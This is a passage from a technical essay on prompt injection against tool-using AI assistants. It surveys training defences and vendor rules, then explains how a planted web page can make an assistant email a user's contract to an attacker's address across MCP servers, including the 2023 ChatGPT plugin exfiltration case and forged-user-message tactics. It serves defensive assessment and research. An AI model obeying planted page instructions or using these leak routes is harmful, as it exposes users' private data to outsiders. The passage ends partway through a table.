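Part of the problem comes from instruction tuning, the stage of training in which a model learns to do what a text asks instead of merely continuing it. The usual training examples teach it to follow instructions wherever they appear. StruQ, the system that Chen and colleagues built, changes both the input format and the examples:

1. A program called the front end receives the instruction and the data separately. It joins them with reserved tokens that have no other use.
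2. The front end deletes anything in the data that would turn into one of these tokens. It repeats the deletion until nothing changes, since removing one piece of text can create another. An attacker therefore cannot forge the boundary.
3. The researchers take a standard set of training examples, each consisting of an instruction, usually some data, and a good answer. They leave half of the examples alone.
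4. In the other half, they add an instruction from a different example to the end of the data. In some of these they first insert a fake answer and fake separators, as if the original task were already finished. The correct answer is still the answer to the original instruction.
5. They train the model on the whole set.

For example, an instruction might ask for a program, and the data might describe a test for prime numbers. The altered version adds a question about dinosaurs to the end of the data, and the model learns to write the program and ignore the question.

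The front end guarantees that outside text cannot forge the separators, much like the guarantee a database placeholder gives. But the model has only learned to ignore instructions between the separators, so it may still follow them. In the researchers' tests, hand-written attacks almost never succeeded against StruQ, but the strongest automated attack succeeded more than half the time.

### SecAlign

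Chen, Chaudhuri and colleagues (2024), in *SecAlign*, attribute StruQ's weakness to what it rewards. StruQ raises the probability of the right answer, $y_w$, to an input *x* that contains an injection. In symbols, it minimises

$$L = -\log p(y_w \mid x)$$

A model can produce so many texts that making one more likely does little to lower the probability of any other particular one. The answer to the injected instruction, $y_l$, can therefore remain fairly probable.

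SecAlign therefore trains on pairs. For each input with an injection, the training set contains the answer to the real instruction (the program) and the answer to the injected one (that dinosaurs are extinct). The procedure has five steps:

1. Start with a model that already follows instructions.
2. Note the separators it uses between instruction, data and response.
3. Choose a public set of instruction examples.
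4. Put an instruction from one example into the data of another. The original answers to the two examples become the preferred and the rejected answer, so nobody has to write or grade anything.
5. Train the model to prefer the first answer to the second.

The last step uses direct preference optimisation, a common method for teaching models which of two answers people like better. It compares the model in training, $\pi_\theta$, with a frozen copy from before the training, $\pi_{\text{ref}}$. For any answer *y*, the ratio

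$$R(y) = \frac{\pi_\theta(y \mid x)}{\pi_{\text{ref}}(y \mid x)}$$

measures how much likelier that answer has become since the start. The training minimises

$$L = -\log \sigma\big(\beta\,[\log R(y_w) - \log R(y_l)]\big)$$

The loss falls as the model makes the right answer more likely relative to the wrong one. As before, σ turns its input into a number between 0 and 1, and the constant β sets how strongly training keeps the model close to the frozen copy.

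In the researchers' comparison, StruQ lowered the average log probability of the wrong answer to about −140, while SecAlign lowered it to about −300 without changing the right answer's probability. SecAlign was also much better than StruQ at resisting automated attacks unlike any in its training. In most of those tests, the attacker tried to make the model print a fixed phrase, and the model had no tools to misuse. Later attacks were more successful, and *May I have your Attention?* (2025) reports breaking defences of this type with attacks designed around the model's architecture.

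### The instruction hierarchy

StruQ and SecAlign divide text only into instructions and data, but an assistant deals with more parties, and some lower-priority text deserves a response. *The Instruction Hierarchy* (Wallace, Xiao and colleagues, 2024), from OpenAI, trained GPT-3.5 Turbo to rank system messages first, then the user's messages, then third-party content such as tool results. In one of its examples, which is close to the running example, a search result contains an instruction to email the user's conversation history to a stranger.

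In their scheme, a lower-ranking instruction counts as aligned if it has the same goals or constraints as the higher ones, and the model should follow it. If it is misaligned, the model should ignore it, or refuse the task if it has no other way to proceed. The researchers made training examples for each case:

- **Aligned instructions.** A language model writes a request with several parts, such as a 20-line poem in Spanish. The researchers split it up, place the parts at different ranks and train the model to answer as if it had received the request whole.
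- **Misaligned instructions.** The researchers train the model to give the answer it would have given had it never seen the lower-ranking instruction.
- **Instructions in search results.** They start from existing examples of web browsing. A second model learns by reinforcement learning to insert instructions into the search results, and it earns a reward when the first model gets confused. The first model then learns to give its original answer regardless.

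The training also improved resistance to injections through tools other than the browser, although the researchers had deliberately left such injections out of the examples. This is some evidence that such training teaches more than a list of known attacks. Wallace and colleagues still expected their models to be vulnerable to powerful attacks.

The researchers knowingly simplified the training by treating every instruction found while browsing as misaligned. By their own definition, though, a link inviting readers to click for a basketball score is an aligned instruction if the user has asked for that score. They wrote that a model that never follows lower-ranking instructions would be immune to injection but much worse at following instructions in general.

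Later work has refined the ranking. *Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* (2026) uses five levels and accounts for the severity of a violation in training. *Trustworthy Agentic AI*, a September 2026 review, concludes that instruction hierarchies reduce the risk but don't eliminate it, and notes that researchers have tested them mainly on models outside deployed agents.

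This kind of training also makes the host's mistakes more harmful. *When Context Gets Root* (2026) points out that a model that has learned to trust high-ranking roles will give more weight to any text the host puts in them by mistake. Wallace and colleagues describe a common example, in which a developer pastes a document into the same message as the request to summarise it. A host that adds web results to the manager's message in this way loses most of the benefit of the training. An assessor can check for this mistake by finding the role marker that precedes the page's text in the exact input to the model.

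### What OpenAI and Anthropic now tell their models

The first version of the Model Spec, OpenAI's published rules for model behaviour, appeared in 2024 and ranked platform rules first, followed by developers, users and tools. According to the passage quoted in the commentary *On OpenAI's Model Spec*, the model must by default treat instructions in tool outputs "as information rather than instructions to follow". In the 2025 revision, according to the commentary *On OpenAI's Model Spec 2.0*, untrusted data ranks last and the model ignores it by default. The October 2025 version of OpenAI's *Model Spec* keeps the ranking and calls it the "chain of command". OpenAI's *Our approach to the Model Spec*, from March 2026, explains that every instruction has an authority level. The chain of command also covers cases in which an agent has to fill in unspecified details while keeping real-world side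 effects under control.

*Claude's Constitution*, by Askell and Carlsmith, names three "principals" whose wishes Anthropic's Claude models should weigh: Anthropic, the operators who build products on the models, and the users. The publisher of a web page is not one of them. Anthropic generally prefers good judgement to strict rules, but it acknowledges that rules make a model harder to manipulate. It favours them where mistakes would be severe, which could well include sending someone's contract to a stranger.

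These documents describe how the companies want their models to behave. Askell and Carlsmith write that Claude's behaviour may not always match the constitution's ideals. If a vendor cites such a document as protection against injection, an assessor still needs to know how often the model fails to behave as intended.

### When the user wants the page followed

Suppose the manager reads the comparison and asks the assistant to order a sample from the best supplier, following the instructions on the supplier's website. On the ordering page, the supplier tells business customers to email the samples desk a delivery address and the reference number of any current supply contract.

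The assistant should now read a web page, search the mailbox for a contract and send information from the contract to an address on the page, which is almost exactly what the attacker wanted in the original example. A model that never followed instructions in web pages would fail the manager. The action is right this time because the manager asked for it, and the model can't tell that from the form of the page's text.

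Suppose the page also asks for a copy of the current contract so that the supplier can match its terms. Some suppliers might ask for this, and some buyers would agree. An attacker who could change or add to the page might insert the same request with a different address. The manager's instruction to follow the page covers the request if the model takes it literally, but may not if the model considers what the manager would want, and the model can't tell from the words alone which reading is right.

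Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026), in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, build their argument on cases of this kind. They use contextual integrity, the philosopher Helen Nissenbaum's theory of privacy, in which a flow of information is appropriate if it fits the norms of its setting. Those norms depend on who sends the information, who receives it, whom it concerns, what kind of information it is and under what conditions it may be shared. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian apply the same questions to an agent's actions. In the printer case, the attacker only needs the agent to accept a false answer to one of them. Sending the contract would be fine if the address really belonged to the supplier, or if the manager really had agreed to share it.

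### The argument that no model can get every case right

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian turn this into a short proof. An agent can verify some of what it observes and must either trust or reject the rest. They consider two situations that look identical to the agent after it has verified all it can. The action is appropriate in one but wrong in the other, where an attacker has produced the same appearance.

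The agent has the same information both times, so it must act with the same probability, *p*, in each. Its chance of carrying out the attack is *p*. Its chance of wrongly blocking the legitimate action is 1 − *p*. Therefore

$$p + (1 - p) = 1$$

and at least one of the two errors has a probability of one half or more. If training lowers *p* to 0.1 for requests to share a contract, the agent falls for one attack in ten and blocks nine legitimate requests in ten. Better training can move *p* up or down, but it cannot shrink the sum.

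The arithmetic is simple, and the argument depends on whether such pairs of situations exist. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian say they have not proved this for every deployment. The problem disappears if the agent can learn from a trusted source which situation it is in. For example, the assistant could ask the manager whether to send the contract, or the host could compare the address with a list of approved suppliers. But the two researchers argue that each check covers only some claims, and an attacker can keep inventing others. They expect such pairs to become more common as agents work with less supervision.

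The title's "may always" is therefore about right for an agent that decides alone. The proof does not rule out a secure assistant, but it shows that wherever such a pair exists, the missing information must come from outside the model. Training on the text of web pages cannot supply it.

They tested how models handle permission by writing 4,200 pairs of business emails that differed in a single clause. In one pair, both emails announce a revised supplier agreement, but one claims that company policy has already authorised the recipient's assistant to send acknowledgements, while the other says only that an automated reply would be fine. The user had asked either for a summary, in which case the assistant should send nothing, or for replies.

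When the user wanted replies, Llama 3.3 70B, an open model, sent them in over 97% of cases. When the user wanted only a summary, it still replied to 54.0% of the emails with the false claim and 49.8% of those without it. The false claim thus made little difference, and the main problem was that the model often replied when the user had not asked it to write to anyone. A version with SecAlign training did worse, replying to 85 to 88% of the emails, although neither model sent anything in response to 4,300 cruder injections from another collection. The system instructions encouraged replies by telling the assistant to send appropriate emails without checking with the user first, and an acknowledgement is much less serious than a leaked contract. Even so, training against injected commands evidently did not teach the model to send emails only when the user wanted it to.

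In a further test, an attacking model revised its emails after each failure and nearly always got the assistant to send something eventually. Its most common method was to forge an earlier message from the user. In one such case, Claude Sonnet 4.6 had identified the original email as an injection but then treated the forged message as the user's own words. A marker alone cannot fix this form of role confusion, because mailboxes do contain genuine messages from the user.

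### Whether a low success rate is enough

A developer could accept all this and still argue that defenses don't have to be perfect. People rely on spam filters and fraud checks, which also make mistakes. If attacks rarely succeed, and succeed less often with each new model, the remaining risk may be acceptable.

This reply is somewhat convincing for the original running example. The manager asked only for a comparison, and no reasonable reading of that request includes sending a contract to anyone. Refusing every such instruction would not make the model less useful, so the trade-off in the proof hardly applies. The same is true of many tests of agents. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) describes a public competition with 41 scenarios, in all of which the harmful action was clearly against the user's interests. Developers can hope to bring the success rate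 of such attacks close to zero.

Clear limits from the user also help. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian gave three models 100 email threads, each containing one task the user had authorised and one message to an outsider that the user had not authorised. Without an explicit limit, GPT-5.2 contacted the outsider in 65% of the threads, GPT-5.4 in 34% and Claude Sonnet 4.6 in 6%. When the user added that outside communication needed approval, the rate fell to 12% for GPT-5.2 and to zero for the other two. This shows that models can respect a stated limit, but the threads contained no attacks, so it is unclear whether they would still do so when someone tries to get around it.

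The reply is weaker when it relies on a single low number. A carrier page costs the attacker almost nothing to leave in place, and any number of assistants may read it. If each reading succeeds with probability *p*, and the readings are independent, the chance of at least one success in *n* readings is

$$1 - (1 - p)^n$$

If an instruction hidden in a web page has a one in a thousand chance of working each time a model reads it, the chance that it works at least once in a thousand readings is about 63%. The same arithmetic applies to spam filters, but a spam message that gets through usually wastes a few seconds of its reader's time, while a contract leaked to a competitor cannot be recalled.

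The rate also depends on the attacker. In Ye and colleagues' experiment, a change of wording raised the agent's rate from 2% to 70%, whereas no input makes a parameterised query more likely to fail. Even an accurate rate, if measured with last year's attacks, can be a poor guide to how the assistant will respond to a page written by someone who has studied it.

The attack success rate may also fall because the model has stopped following instructions on any web page, including the supplier's ordering page. Once the developer teaches it to follow such pages when the user asks, the ambiguous cases return. A low rate can therefore be enough for an assistant that does narrow tasks and can do little damage, but one that can read and send a user's email should have safeguards beyond the model's training.

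An assessor can test a product for this with a small version of the paired-email test. The assessor publishes a harmless page on an obscure subject, including a request that readers send a one-line acknowledgement to an address the assessor controls. The assessor then asks the assistant to summarise the page and, separately, to follow the page's instructions. If the assistant sends the acknowledgement when asked only for a summary, it is following instructions that the user never told it to follow. If it refuses when asked to follow them, some of its resistance probably comes from ignoring instructions in pages altogether. The assessor should repeat both requests many times and write the page's request in several different styles, since passing with one wording is weak evidence that the assistant will pass with another.

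## Why a search server without permissions does not limit the harm

Training lowers the chance that the model follows a planted instruction but does not remove it, so the possible damage depends on what the assistant can do after reading one. In the running example, the planted text comes in through a search server that holds no credentials and can only look up public pages. The harm can still go beyond a bad answer, such as a comparison that favours a dishonest supplier, because the assistant also has access to email.

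The search server does lack permissions, but this does not limit the harm, because a server's permissions restrict only what that server can do. In the attack, the search server only returns search results. The mail server, which has all the permissions it needs, sends the contract.

Reviews that examine one server at a time make it easy to assume that a search server without permissions can do little harm. *MCP-in-SoS* (2026), a framework for scoring the risks of open-source MCP servers, treats the server as the security boundary and whatever calls it as an untrusted requester. *Exposed by Design* (2026), a scan of MCP servers on the public internet, looks for flaws that would let an outsider run commands or steal credentials. It explicitly excludes indirect prompt injection, on the grounds that it targets the AI client rather than the server. Both are sensible ways to find faulty servers,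 but a search server could pass both reviews with no findings, and the assessor would still not know whether a web page could make the assistant send the manager's email to a stranger.

### Permissions add up within a session

Each server gives the assistant a set of permissions. In the running example, the sets are

$$P_{\text{search}} = \{\text{search the web}\}$$

$$P_{\text{mail}} = \{\text{search mail},\ \text{read mail},\ \text{send mail}\}$$

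The model can write a call to any of these tools, so the assistant's authority *A* is the union of the two sets:

$$A = P_{\text{search}} \cup P_{\text{mail}}$$

The model writes every call based on its whole context, which includes text from both servers. A search result can therefore lead to any action in *A*, whereas the mistaken inference assumes it can lead only to actions in the first set. Running the search server in a sandbox or removing its access to local files would not change the mail permissions.

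Text from one server can influence a call to another, and the number of these routes grows quickly as servers are added. With *n* servers there are *n*(*n* − 1) routes. Two servers have two routes, from search to mail and from mail to search, and ten servers have 90.

Users usually want these routes. If the manager asks the assistant to find a supplier's address and write to it, text from the search server has to determine where the email goes. Data also crosses between servers when there is no attack. *MCPHunt* (2026) gave five models 147 tasks that involved several MCP servers, such as moving a project from one directory to another. The models carried credentials across a trust boundary while doing what the user had asked, because the tasks required reading from one system and writing to another. A host that blocked all movement between servers would be safer, but there would be little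 reason to connect more than one server to it.

### What the attack needs from the search server

The search server lacks almost everything that a security reviewer would worry about. The attack does not depend on any of it:

| Item | Does the search server have it? | How the attack manages |
|---|---|---|
| The credentials for the mailbox | No | The mail server uses its own |
| A connection to the mail server | No | The host already has one |
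| The conversation with the manager | No | The planted text works without referring to it |
| A list of the other connected tools | No | The model has the list in its context |
| The ability to return text from a web page | Yes | The model reads the planted instructions |

Only the last item matters, and a search server without it would be useless.

*Parasites in the Toolchain* (Zhao, Hou and colleagues, 2025) makes similar assumptions. The attacker can put text where one of the victim's tools will retrieve it and has an address for receiving stolen data. The attacker can't compromise the host, the model or any server, and doesn't know which files or servers the victim has. In one example, a user asks for recent social media posts on a subject. One of the posts causes the assistant to read a configuration file containing access keys and email it to a stranger, even though each component would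 pass a security check on its own.

### Where MCP's isolation stops

MCP isolates servers from each other, which protects against some attacks. An attacker who took over the search server could not use it to call the mail server directly or download the conversation.

But the isolation does not restrict what the model does with the text a server returns. One stated aim of the current Model Context Protocol specification is to let people combine servers seamlessly, and the shared context makes this possible.

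The July 2026 version of the Model Context Protocol made the shared context even more important. According to *Key Changes* (Model Context Protocol, 2026), a server that needs to track something across calls now issues a handle, which later calls include as an ordinary argument. Since the model writes the arguments, these handles will normally also pass through the shared context.

Web browsers address a related problem with the same-origin policy, which generally prevents a script from one site from reading another site's data. *MCP-DPT* (2026), which classifies MCP defences by where they belong, identifies the lack of such a policy as the cause of attacks in which one server manipulates another's tools. A browser can enforce this policy because it tracks which site each script came from. A host can identify which server returned each result, but not which parts of the context caused the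 model to write a particular tool call.

*MCP-38* (2026), a taxonomy of MCP threats, describes a cross-server attack in which a malicious server's responses stay in the context and change how the agent uses a trusted server's tools, for example by adding a blind-copy recipient to an email. The malicious server never calls the trusted tool. A search server that isn't malicious can have the same effect if it returns a page containing malicious instructions. *Unsafe by Flow* (2026) assumes that honest parties built the host, the client and the server, but still treats outside content in a tool's output as a security risk because that content may affect later tool calls.

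It is also unclear who should prevent this. *Formal Security Analysis of Agent Protocol Composition* (Zheng, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) discusses a case reported by the security company Snyk, in which an agent is connected to one server that fetches web pages and another that converts files into text. A web page leads the agent to read a local file through the converter and send its contents out through the fetcher. Each server's maintainers can fix bugs in their own code, but neither group can enforce a rule that web content must not cause a file to leave the computer, because each server handles only part of the sequence.

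To find more failures of this kind, Zheng and colleagues turned the documentation of five agent protocols, including MCP, into formal models. A program searched these models for sequences of steps that break a security property, and the researchers replayed sequences on real software where they could. They found 35 problems in the individual protocols and another 30 that appeared only when protocols were combined. None of the protocols made anyone responsible for enforcing security across the combination. The 30 failures are good evidence that checking the parts separately misses failures of the whole. They are not a count of leaks like the one in the running example, because they arose from connecting different protocols and the researchers' checks include some properties that no documentation requires.

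### The ChatGPT plugin case of 2023

In May 2023, Johann Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, demonstrated the whole attack in ChatGPT, from a web page to a leaked email. ChatGPT then supported plugins, add-ons from other companies that the model could call much as it calls MCP tools today. His post *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained* describes a user with two plugins. WebPilot fetched web pages, and Zapier connected ChatGPT to other services and could read the user's Gmail.

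The user asked ChatGPT to visit a page where Rehberger had planted instructions. ChatGPT used Zapier to retrieve the latest email and summarised it. It then added the summary to a web address Rehberger controlled and had WebPilot request that address, which delivered the summary to him. Willison (2023), in *Let ChatGPT visit a website and have your email stolen*, called it the first working proof of concept he had seen of a plugin attack that stole private data.

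WebPilot had no access to the mailbox, but it brought in the instructions and later sent out the stolen text. Both times, it only fetched a web page. An assessor who rated it by its permissions, as "read-only, public pages", would have underestimated the risk.

Rehberger had noticed the underlying behaviour earlier, when text on a website made ChatGPT search for flights through the travel company Expedia's plugin. A journalist reproduced this in the Tom's Hardware article *ChatGPT Plugins Open Security Holes From PDFs, Websites and More*. ChatGPT summarised the page correctly, then launched the Expedia plugin without asking and recommended three flights. It didn't book any of them, but the test confirmed that a page read through one plugin could trigger another.

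Rehberger called the attack cross-plugin request forgery, after cross-site request forgery, in which a malicious page makes a visitor's browser send a request to another site where the visitor is logged in. In the browser version, the attacker usually can't see the response, so the main danger is requests that change something, such as a password or a setting. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Removes the "Chat with Code" Plugin From Store* points out that with plugins, reading is dangerous too, because ChatGPT can send what it has read to the attacker. A read-only mail connection would not have stopped the 2023 attack, because the attack never used Zapier to send anything.

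Zapier fixed the problem in its own plugin, which had the authority to act, by requiring the user to confirm the action. The confirmation had to be authenticated because an attacker could otherwise have instructed ChatGPT to click the confirmation link.

The case is a single demonstration on a model from 2023, so it doesn't show how often such an attack would succeed now. OpenAI has also replaced the plugins, but both their replacement and MCP let one model call tools from several providers, and Embrace The Red considers them exposed to the same threat.

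### The confused deputy

The theory behind this problem is older than language models. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) tells a nearly true story about the computing company Tymshare and its compiler, a program that translates other programs. The compiler let users name a file for debugging output. It also recorded statistics in a file in its own directory, so the company had given it permission to write to any file there. The same directory held the company's billing records. A user who had learned the billing file's name entered it as the file for debugging output, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

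The user never had the right to change the billing file. The compiler had that right, and the user only supplied the file's name. In the running example, whoever wrote the carrier page has no right to send the manager's mail and likewise supplies little more than an address, collector@attacker.example. The assistant uses the manager's authority to send the message there.

Hardy asks who was to blame and finds no obvious answer. The code that wrote the debugging output was correct, since users had good reasons to name files in other directories. It became unsafe only when the company added the licence. Similarly, the search server correctly returns what is on the page, and the mail server correctly accepts outside addresses, because purchasing managers write to outsiders every day. The assistant became dangerous when someone connected the mail server, even though nobody changed the search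 server's code. An earlier approval of the search server may still be correct about that server alone, but the assessor can't rely on it for the new session.

According to Hardy, the compiler had authority from two sources, the company and the user, and no way to keep them apart. Tymshare first added a command that let the compiler choose which authority to use for each action. This complicated the system, and some programs turned out to need more than two authorities. Hardy preferred capabilities, which are objects that both identify a resource and grant the right to use it. The compiler would hold a capability for the statistics file, and users would pass it one for their output file. No user could pass it a capability for the billing file, because no user would have one.

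A mail tool could similarly accept only tokens for recipients the manager had chosen for the current task, rather than any address as text. The carrier page could contain the attacker's address but not a valid token for it, so step 7 of the attack would fail. The assistant could still send the contract to the wrong approved recipient.

The compiler followed fixed code, so its programmers could specify which authority each line should use. A model's actions instead depend on the text it receives, and it cannot reliably distinguish the manager's text from other text. Requiring the model to state on whose behalf it is making each call would therefore not solve the problem.

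The term "confused deputy" can also mislead an assessor. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* uses it for a flaw in servers that connect to other companies' services, which lets attackers obtain login authorisation without the user's consent. A vendor who has followed that section has fixed the login flaw, but the attack in the running example would still work.

### Confinement

In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) asked how a customer can let someone else's program process private data without the program leaking it. He noted that the program may do its job badly, which leaves the customer with wrong output as evidence, or it may leak the data, generally without any sign. The mistaken inference about the search server accounts only for bad output. The manager might notice a poor comparison of label printers, but a leaked contract doesn't change the comparison.

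Lampson described confinement as a constraint on a program while it runs, rather than a property of the program. The simplest such constraint forbids the program to call any other program, but he considered this impractical. His alternative, a transitivity rule, requires any program that a confined program calls to be either trusted or confined as well.

In the running example, the program to confine is the assistant, because it handles the private mail. The rule therefore concerns the programs that the assistant calls. The mail server can't be confined because its purpose is to deliver messages to other people, so it would have to be trusted. By Lampson's definition, that means the customer must believe that the program will neither leak the data nor help its caller to do so. An honest mail server won't leak the data itself, but it fails this test because it delivers whatever the assistant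 sends, to any address. The search server also fails if an outsider can read the queries or page requests that the assistant sends through it.

Lampson proposed that the customer should determine what goes into the channels a program needs for its work. His example is the bill for the service, in which a program could encode stolen data. If the customer can calculate the bill in advance, the program cannot hide anything in it. For the assistant, the manager would have to fix the recipient and content of each message. That is reasonable for a few important emails but defeats the purpose of an assistant that writes routine ones.

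### Two flows that meet in the context

Access rights determine who may open what. In *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, Denning (1976) objected that most systems checked each access separately and ignored the paths that permitted accesses create together. Her model gives every piece of data a security class and defines which flows between classes are allowed. If information may flow from class A to class B and from B to C, it may in effect flow from A to C, because a program can make the two moves in sequence.

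The mail permissions in the running example allow two flows:

$$\text{mailbox} \to \text{context} \qquad \text{context} \to \text{outside address}$$

Together they allow a third:

$$\text{mailbox} \to \text{outside address}$$

The manager may have agreed to each of the first two without considering the third. The search server is not part of any of the three, so restricting its permissions cannot block the path the contract takes.

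Denning's rule would interrupt it. Take two classes, public (*L*) and confidential (*H*), with the requirement that confidential data must not flow into anything public. When a program combines data from several classes, the result belongs to the lowest class that is at least as high as all of them. Denning writes this combination as ⊕. After the model has read the web page and the contract, the class of the context is

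$$L \oplus H = H$$

The attacker's address is public, so the rule forbids sending it anything from the context. But the rule allows the model to read the carrier page, because public data may flow anywhere.

The page contributes influence rather than secrets, and a different kind of rule covers this. Integrity rules ask how far the system can trust the source of a piece of data, and security engineers know the standard set as the Biba model. In one version, the low-water mark policy, every program *s* and every piece of data *o* has an integrity level *i*. When the program reads the data, its level falls to the lower of the two:

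$$i_{\text{new}}(s) = \min\big(i(s),\ i(o)\big)$$

No program may change data or call programs above its own level. The assistant starts at a high level because it is working from the manager's request. After reading a page that anyone could have written, it drops to a low level and may no longer call the mail server.

Permissions and the two kinds of flow rule give different answers at each stage of the attack:

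| Action | Permissions of each server | Secrecy rule (Denning) | Integrity rule (low-water mark) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read the carrier page | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed, but the context drops to low integrity |
| Read the contract email | Allowed | Allowed, but the context becomes confidential | Forbidden |
| Send it to the outside address | Allowed | Forbidden | Forbidden |

The Biba model also includes a looser version called the ring policy, which lets a program read anything without losing its integrity level and relies on the program to check what it has read. The host in the running example in effect follows this policy, because it lets the model read any page and keep its access to the mail tools, and relies on the model to ignore planted instructions. This would be acceptable if the model could ignore them reliably.

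The stricter rules would also block legitimate work, which helps explain why a host might not apply them. The secrecy rule would stop the manager from sending a contract to the supplier who is supposed to sign it. Under the low-water mark policy, the assistant could not look up a supplier's address and then write to the supplier. Once a program has dropped to a low level, it stays there until it restarts.

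The labels are cruder for a language model than for an ordinary program. Denning could follow data from one variable to the next, but any part of a model's context may affect any call the model writes. The host therefore has to give the context a single label, and one web page lowers the integrity of the whole context.

### The lethal trifecta

The three capabilities in Willison's lethal trifecta are where these flows begin and end. The influence starts with the untrusted text, while the leak starts with the private data and ends with the means of communicating with the outside. The attack in the running example fails if any one of them is missing. Without untrusted text, nobody outside can give the model instructions, and without private data, there is nothing worth stealing. If there is no way to send data out, the model may still do harm, such as deleting mail, but the attacker does not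 receive the mail.

Willison listed more than a dozen products in which researchers demonstrated data theft of this kind, including ChatGPT, Google Bard, Slack and several versions of Microsoft's Copilot. The vendors fixed almost all of these flaws promptly, usually by blocking the route the data left by. He warned that such fixes do not help people who combine tools themselves, because no vendor is responsible for the combination.

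In a March 2026 post, the Model Context Protocol maintainers wrote that because users routinely combine tools from several servers, the risk profile is "a property of the session, not of any single server". In their example, whether a tool that searches email is safe depends on which other tools the agent has. On this view, approving servers one by one can't establish that an assistant is safe.

The same post describes a demonstration that combined a malicious Google Calendar event, a calendar server and a tool that runs code on the user's computer. The code tool mattered most because an agent that can run any command needs only one planted instruction to leak data, whether the tool came from an MCP server or was already part of the host. An assessor who lists only the connected servers could therefore miss the most dangerous tool in the session.

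### Counting the combinations

The trifecta gives an assessor a way to audit a session. The assessor lists every tool, including those built into the host, and marks which tools return text that outsiders could have written, which read private data and which can carry data out. Each combination of one tool from each list is a possible path for a leak. With *u* sources of outsiders' text, *p* tools that read private data and *o* outward channels, the number of combinations is

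$$N = u \times p \times o$$

Suppose the purchasing department has added more servers to the manager's assistant, and that each tool has only one role for now:

| Returns outsiders' text | Reads private data | Carries data out |
|---|---|---|
| Web search | Mail reader | Mail sender |
| Supplier reviews | Company documents | Posts in a chat shared with suppliers |
| Messages from a public contact form | | |

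This gives 3 × 2 × 2 = 12 combinations. The running example combines web search, a mail reader and a mail sender. In another, a planted supplier review leads the assistant to copy a confidential price list from the company's documents into the shared chat.

Connecting a fourth source of outsiders' text would add 1 × 2 × 2 = 4 combinations, even if its server had permission only to return public text. In the original set, closing one of the two outward channels would remove 3 × 2 × 1 = 6 combinations. Disconnecting web search would remove four and leave eight, because reviews and contact-form messages could still bring in instructions.

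Reviewing each server separately misses all twelve. The search server has a tool in the first column only. The mail server has tools in the second and third, which is normal for mail. No server has tools in all three columns, so each one passes.

The number of combinations is useful as a checklist, but it doesn't measure risk. A combination that involves the whole mailbox counts the same as one that involves a folder of old price lists, and some sources are much easier to attack than others. Going from twelve combinations to six does not halve the risk if the remaining outward channel can send email to anyone. Only a count of zero has a definite meaning, and only if the assessor has found every tool's roles. Reaching zero requires emptying one of the columns. Lampson warned that there is probably no rigorous way to identify every channel in a system of even moderate complexity.

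Tools that can play a part in such attacks are common. Zhao and colleagues examined 12,230 tools on 1,360 public MCP servers and classed 1,062 of the tools (8.7%), spread over 370 servers (27.2%), as exploitable for their attack. These counts don't measure how many people are exposed, because that depends on which servers each person has connected in the same session.

An assessor can check whether the search server's lack of permissions limits the harm without staging an attack. Using a test account, the assessor directly asks the assistant to search the web, then find a specific harmless message in the mailbox and send it to an outside address the assessor controls. If the message arrives without any further check, the host allows the complete path, and only the model's judgement would stop instructions in a web page from using it to leak email. The search server's lack of permissions therefore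 doesn't limit the harm. The usual injection test can't settle this, since the attack may fail only because the model recognised that particular attack.

### Least privilege on the mail server

A security engineer may object that this argument underrates least privilege, the principle that a program should have only the permissions it needs. It is one of the oldest and most effective ways to limit damage, and Zhao and colleagues name its absence as one of two root causes of the attacks they describe. The other is that outside text can directly influence tool calls.

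The objection is correct, as long as the limits apply to the mail server. The assistant has the permissions of both servers, and nearly all the harmful ones come from the mail server. If the mail server can read only a folder of supplier quotes, an attacker can't get a contract from another folder. If it can save drafts but not send them, the assistant can't email anything to a stranger. If it can send only within the company, the assistant can't send mail to the attacker's outside address. The search server in the example already has as few permissions as possible, so applying least privilege to it can't reduce the harm further.

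These limits still leave some risk. A manager who wants the assistant to answer suppliers must let it send mail outside the company, just as Tymshare's compiler needed to write to its own directory. Any permission kept for legitimate work can also be misused. Even without permission to send mail, an assistant that can read it may be able to leak the text through another tool, as the 2023 case showed. Gaire and colleagues describe the same problem from the input side, where read-only access to a source of text leads to actions that change something elsewhere.

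### Strangers can already write to the mailbox

The other objection is that web search makes little difference, since anyone who knows the manager's address can send an email with planted instructions. Willison makes this point too, and calls a mail tool a perfect source of untrusted content. One server can even have all three parts of the trifecta. His example is GitHub's MCP server, which could read public issues written by strangers and private repositories, and create pull requests that could leak private data.

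This objection shows that the audit above undercounted the combinations. The mail reader also returns text written by outsiders, so it belongs in the first column as well as the second. Adding it as a fourth source brings the total to 16. One of the four new combinations lies entirely within the mail server, which receives the instructions, reads the private mail and sends it out. A careful review of that server alone could find this combination, but the other 15 involve more than one server.

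Removing web search would therefore not make the assistant safe, because an attacker can still send it instructions by email. But web search does make the attack easier. An attacker using email has to choose a target, know the address and get a message past the spam filter, and the assistant then has to open it. A web page carrying the instructions can reach any assistant whose user asks about label printers, including users the attacker has never heard of.

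The host also has more information for filtering email than for filtering search results. The company's mail system can often verify the domain a message came from. The host could, for example, let the model read messages from colleagues but not from unknown senders. People use web search to find pages by strangers, so a similar rule would exclude most of the results. An email also usually stays in the mailbox, where an investigator can find it later, while an attacker can change a web page at any time.

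Email suits an attacker who wants one particular company's contracts, because the attacker can write to the right person and mention a real project. Web search is less useful to such an attacker, though a page on a narrow subject that only a few buyers look up could also work.

The audit formula gives a rough idea of the difference for the original pair of servers. The mail server alone provides one source, one tool that reads private data and one outward channel, which makes one combination. Connecting the search server adds a second source, making two combinations. If an outsider can also read the assistant's searches or page requests, there is a second outward channel, and the total is 2 × 1 × 2 = 4.

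## The routes by which mail can leave

In the running example, the mail server's send tool is the obvious route out. But in the 2023 ChatGPT plugin case, the stolen summary left through a tool that fetched web pages, and other assistants have leaked data through images in the chat window. An assessor who looks only for tools designed to send data will miss these routes.

A channel exists wherever the model can influence something that an outsider can observe. An assessor can list the channels by following everything the model writes. Some of it goes into tool calls, which the host passes to the servers, and some goes into the reply, which the chat window displays. Some assistants also save files or settings that other programs process later. In each case the assessor asks which program contacts an outside system next, how much of that contact the model controls, and who is at the other end.

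For the manager's assistant, this gives the following list:

| Channel | Who receives the data | Would the manager see it? | What closes it |
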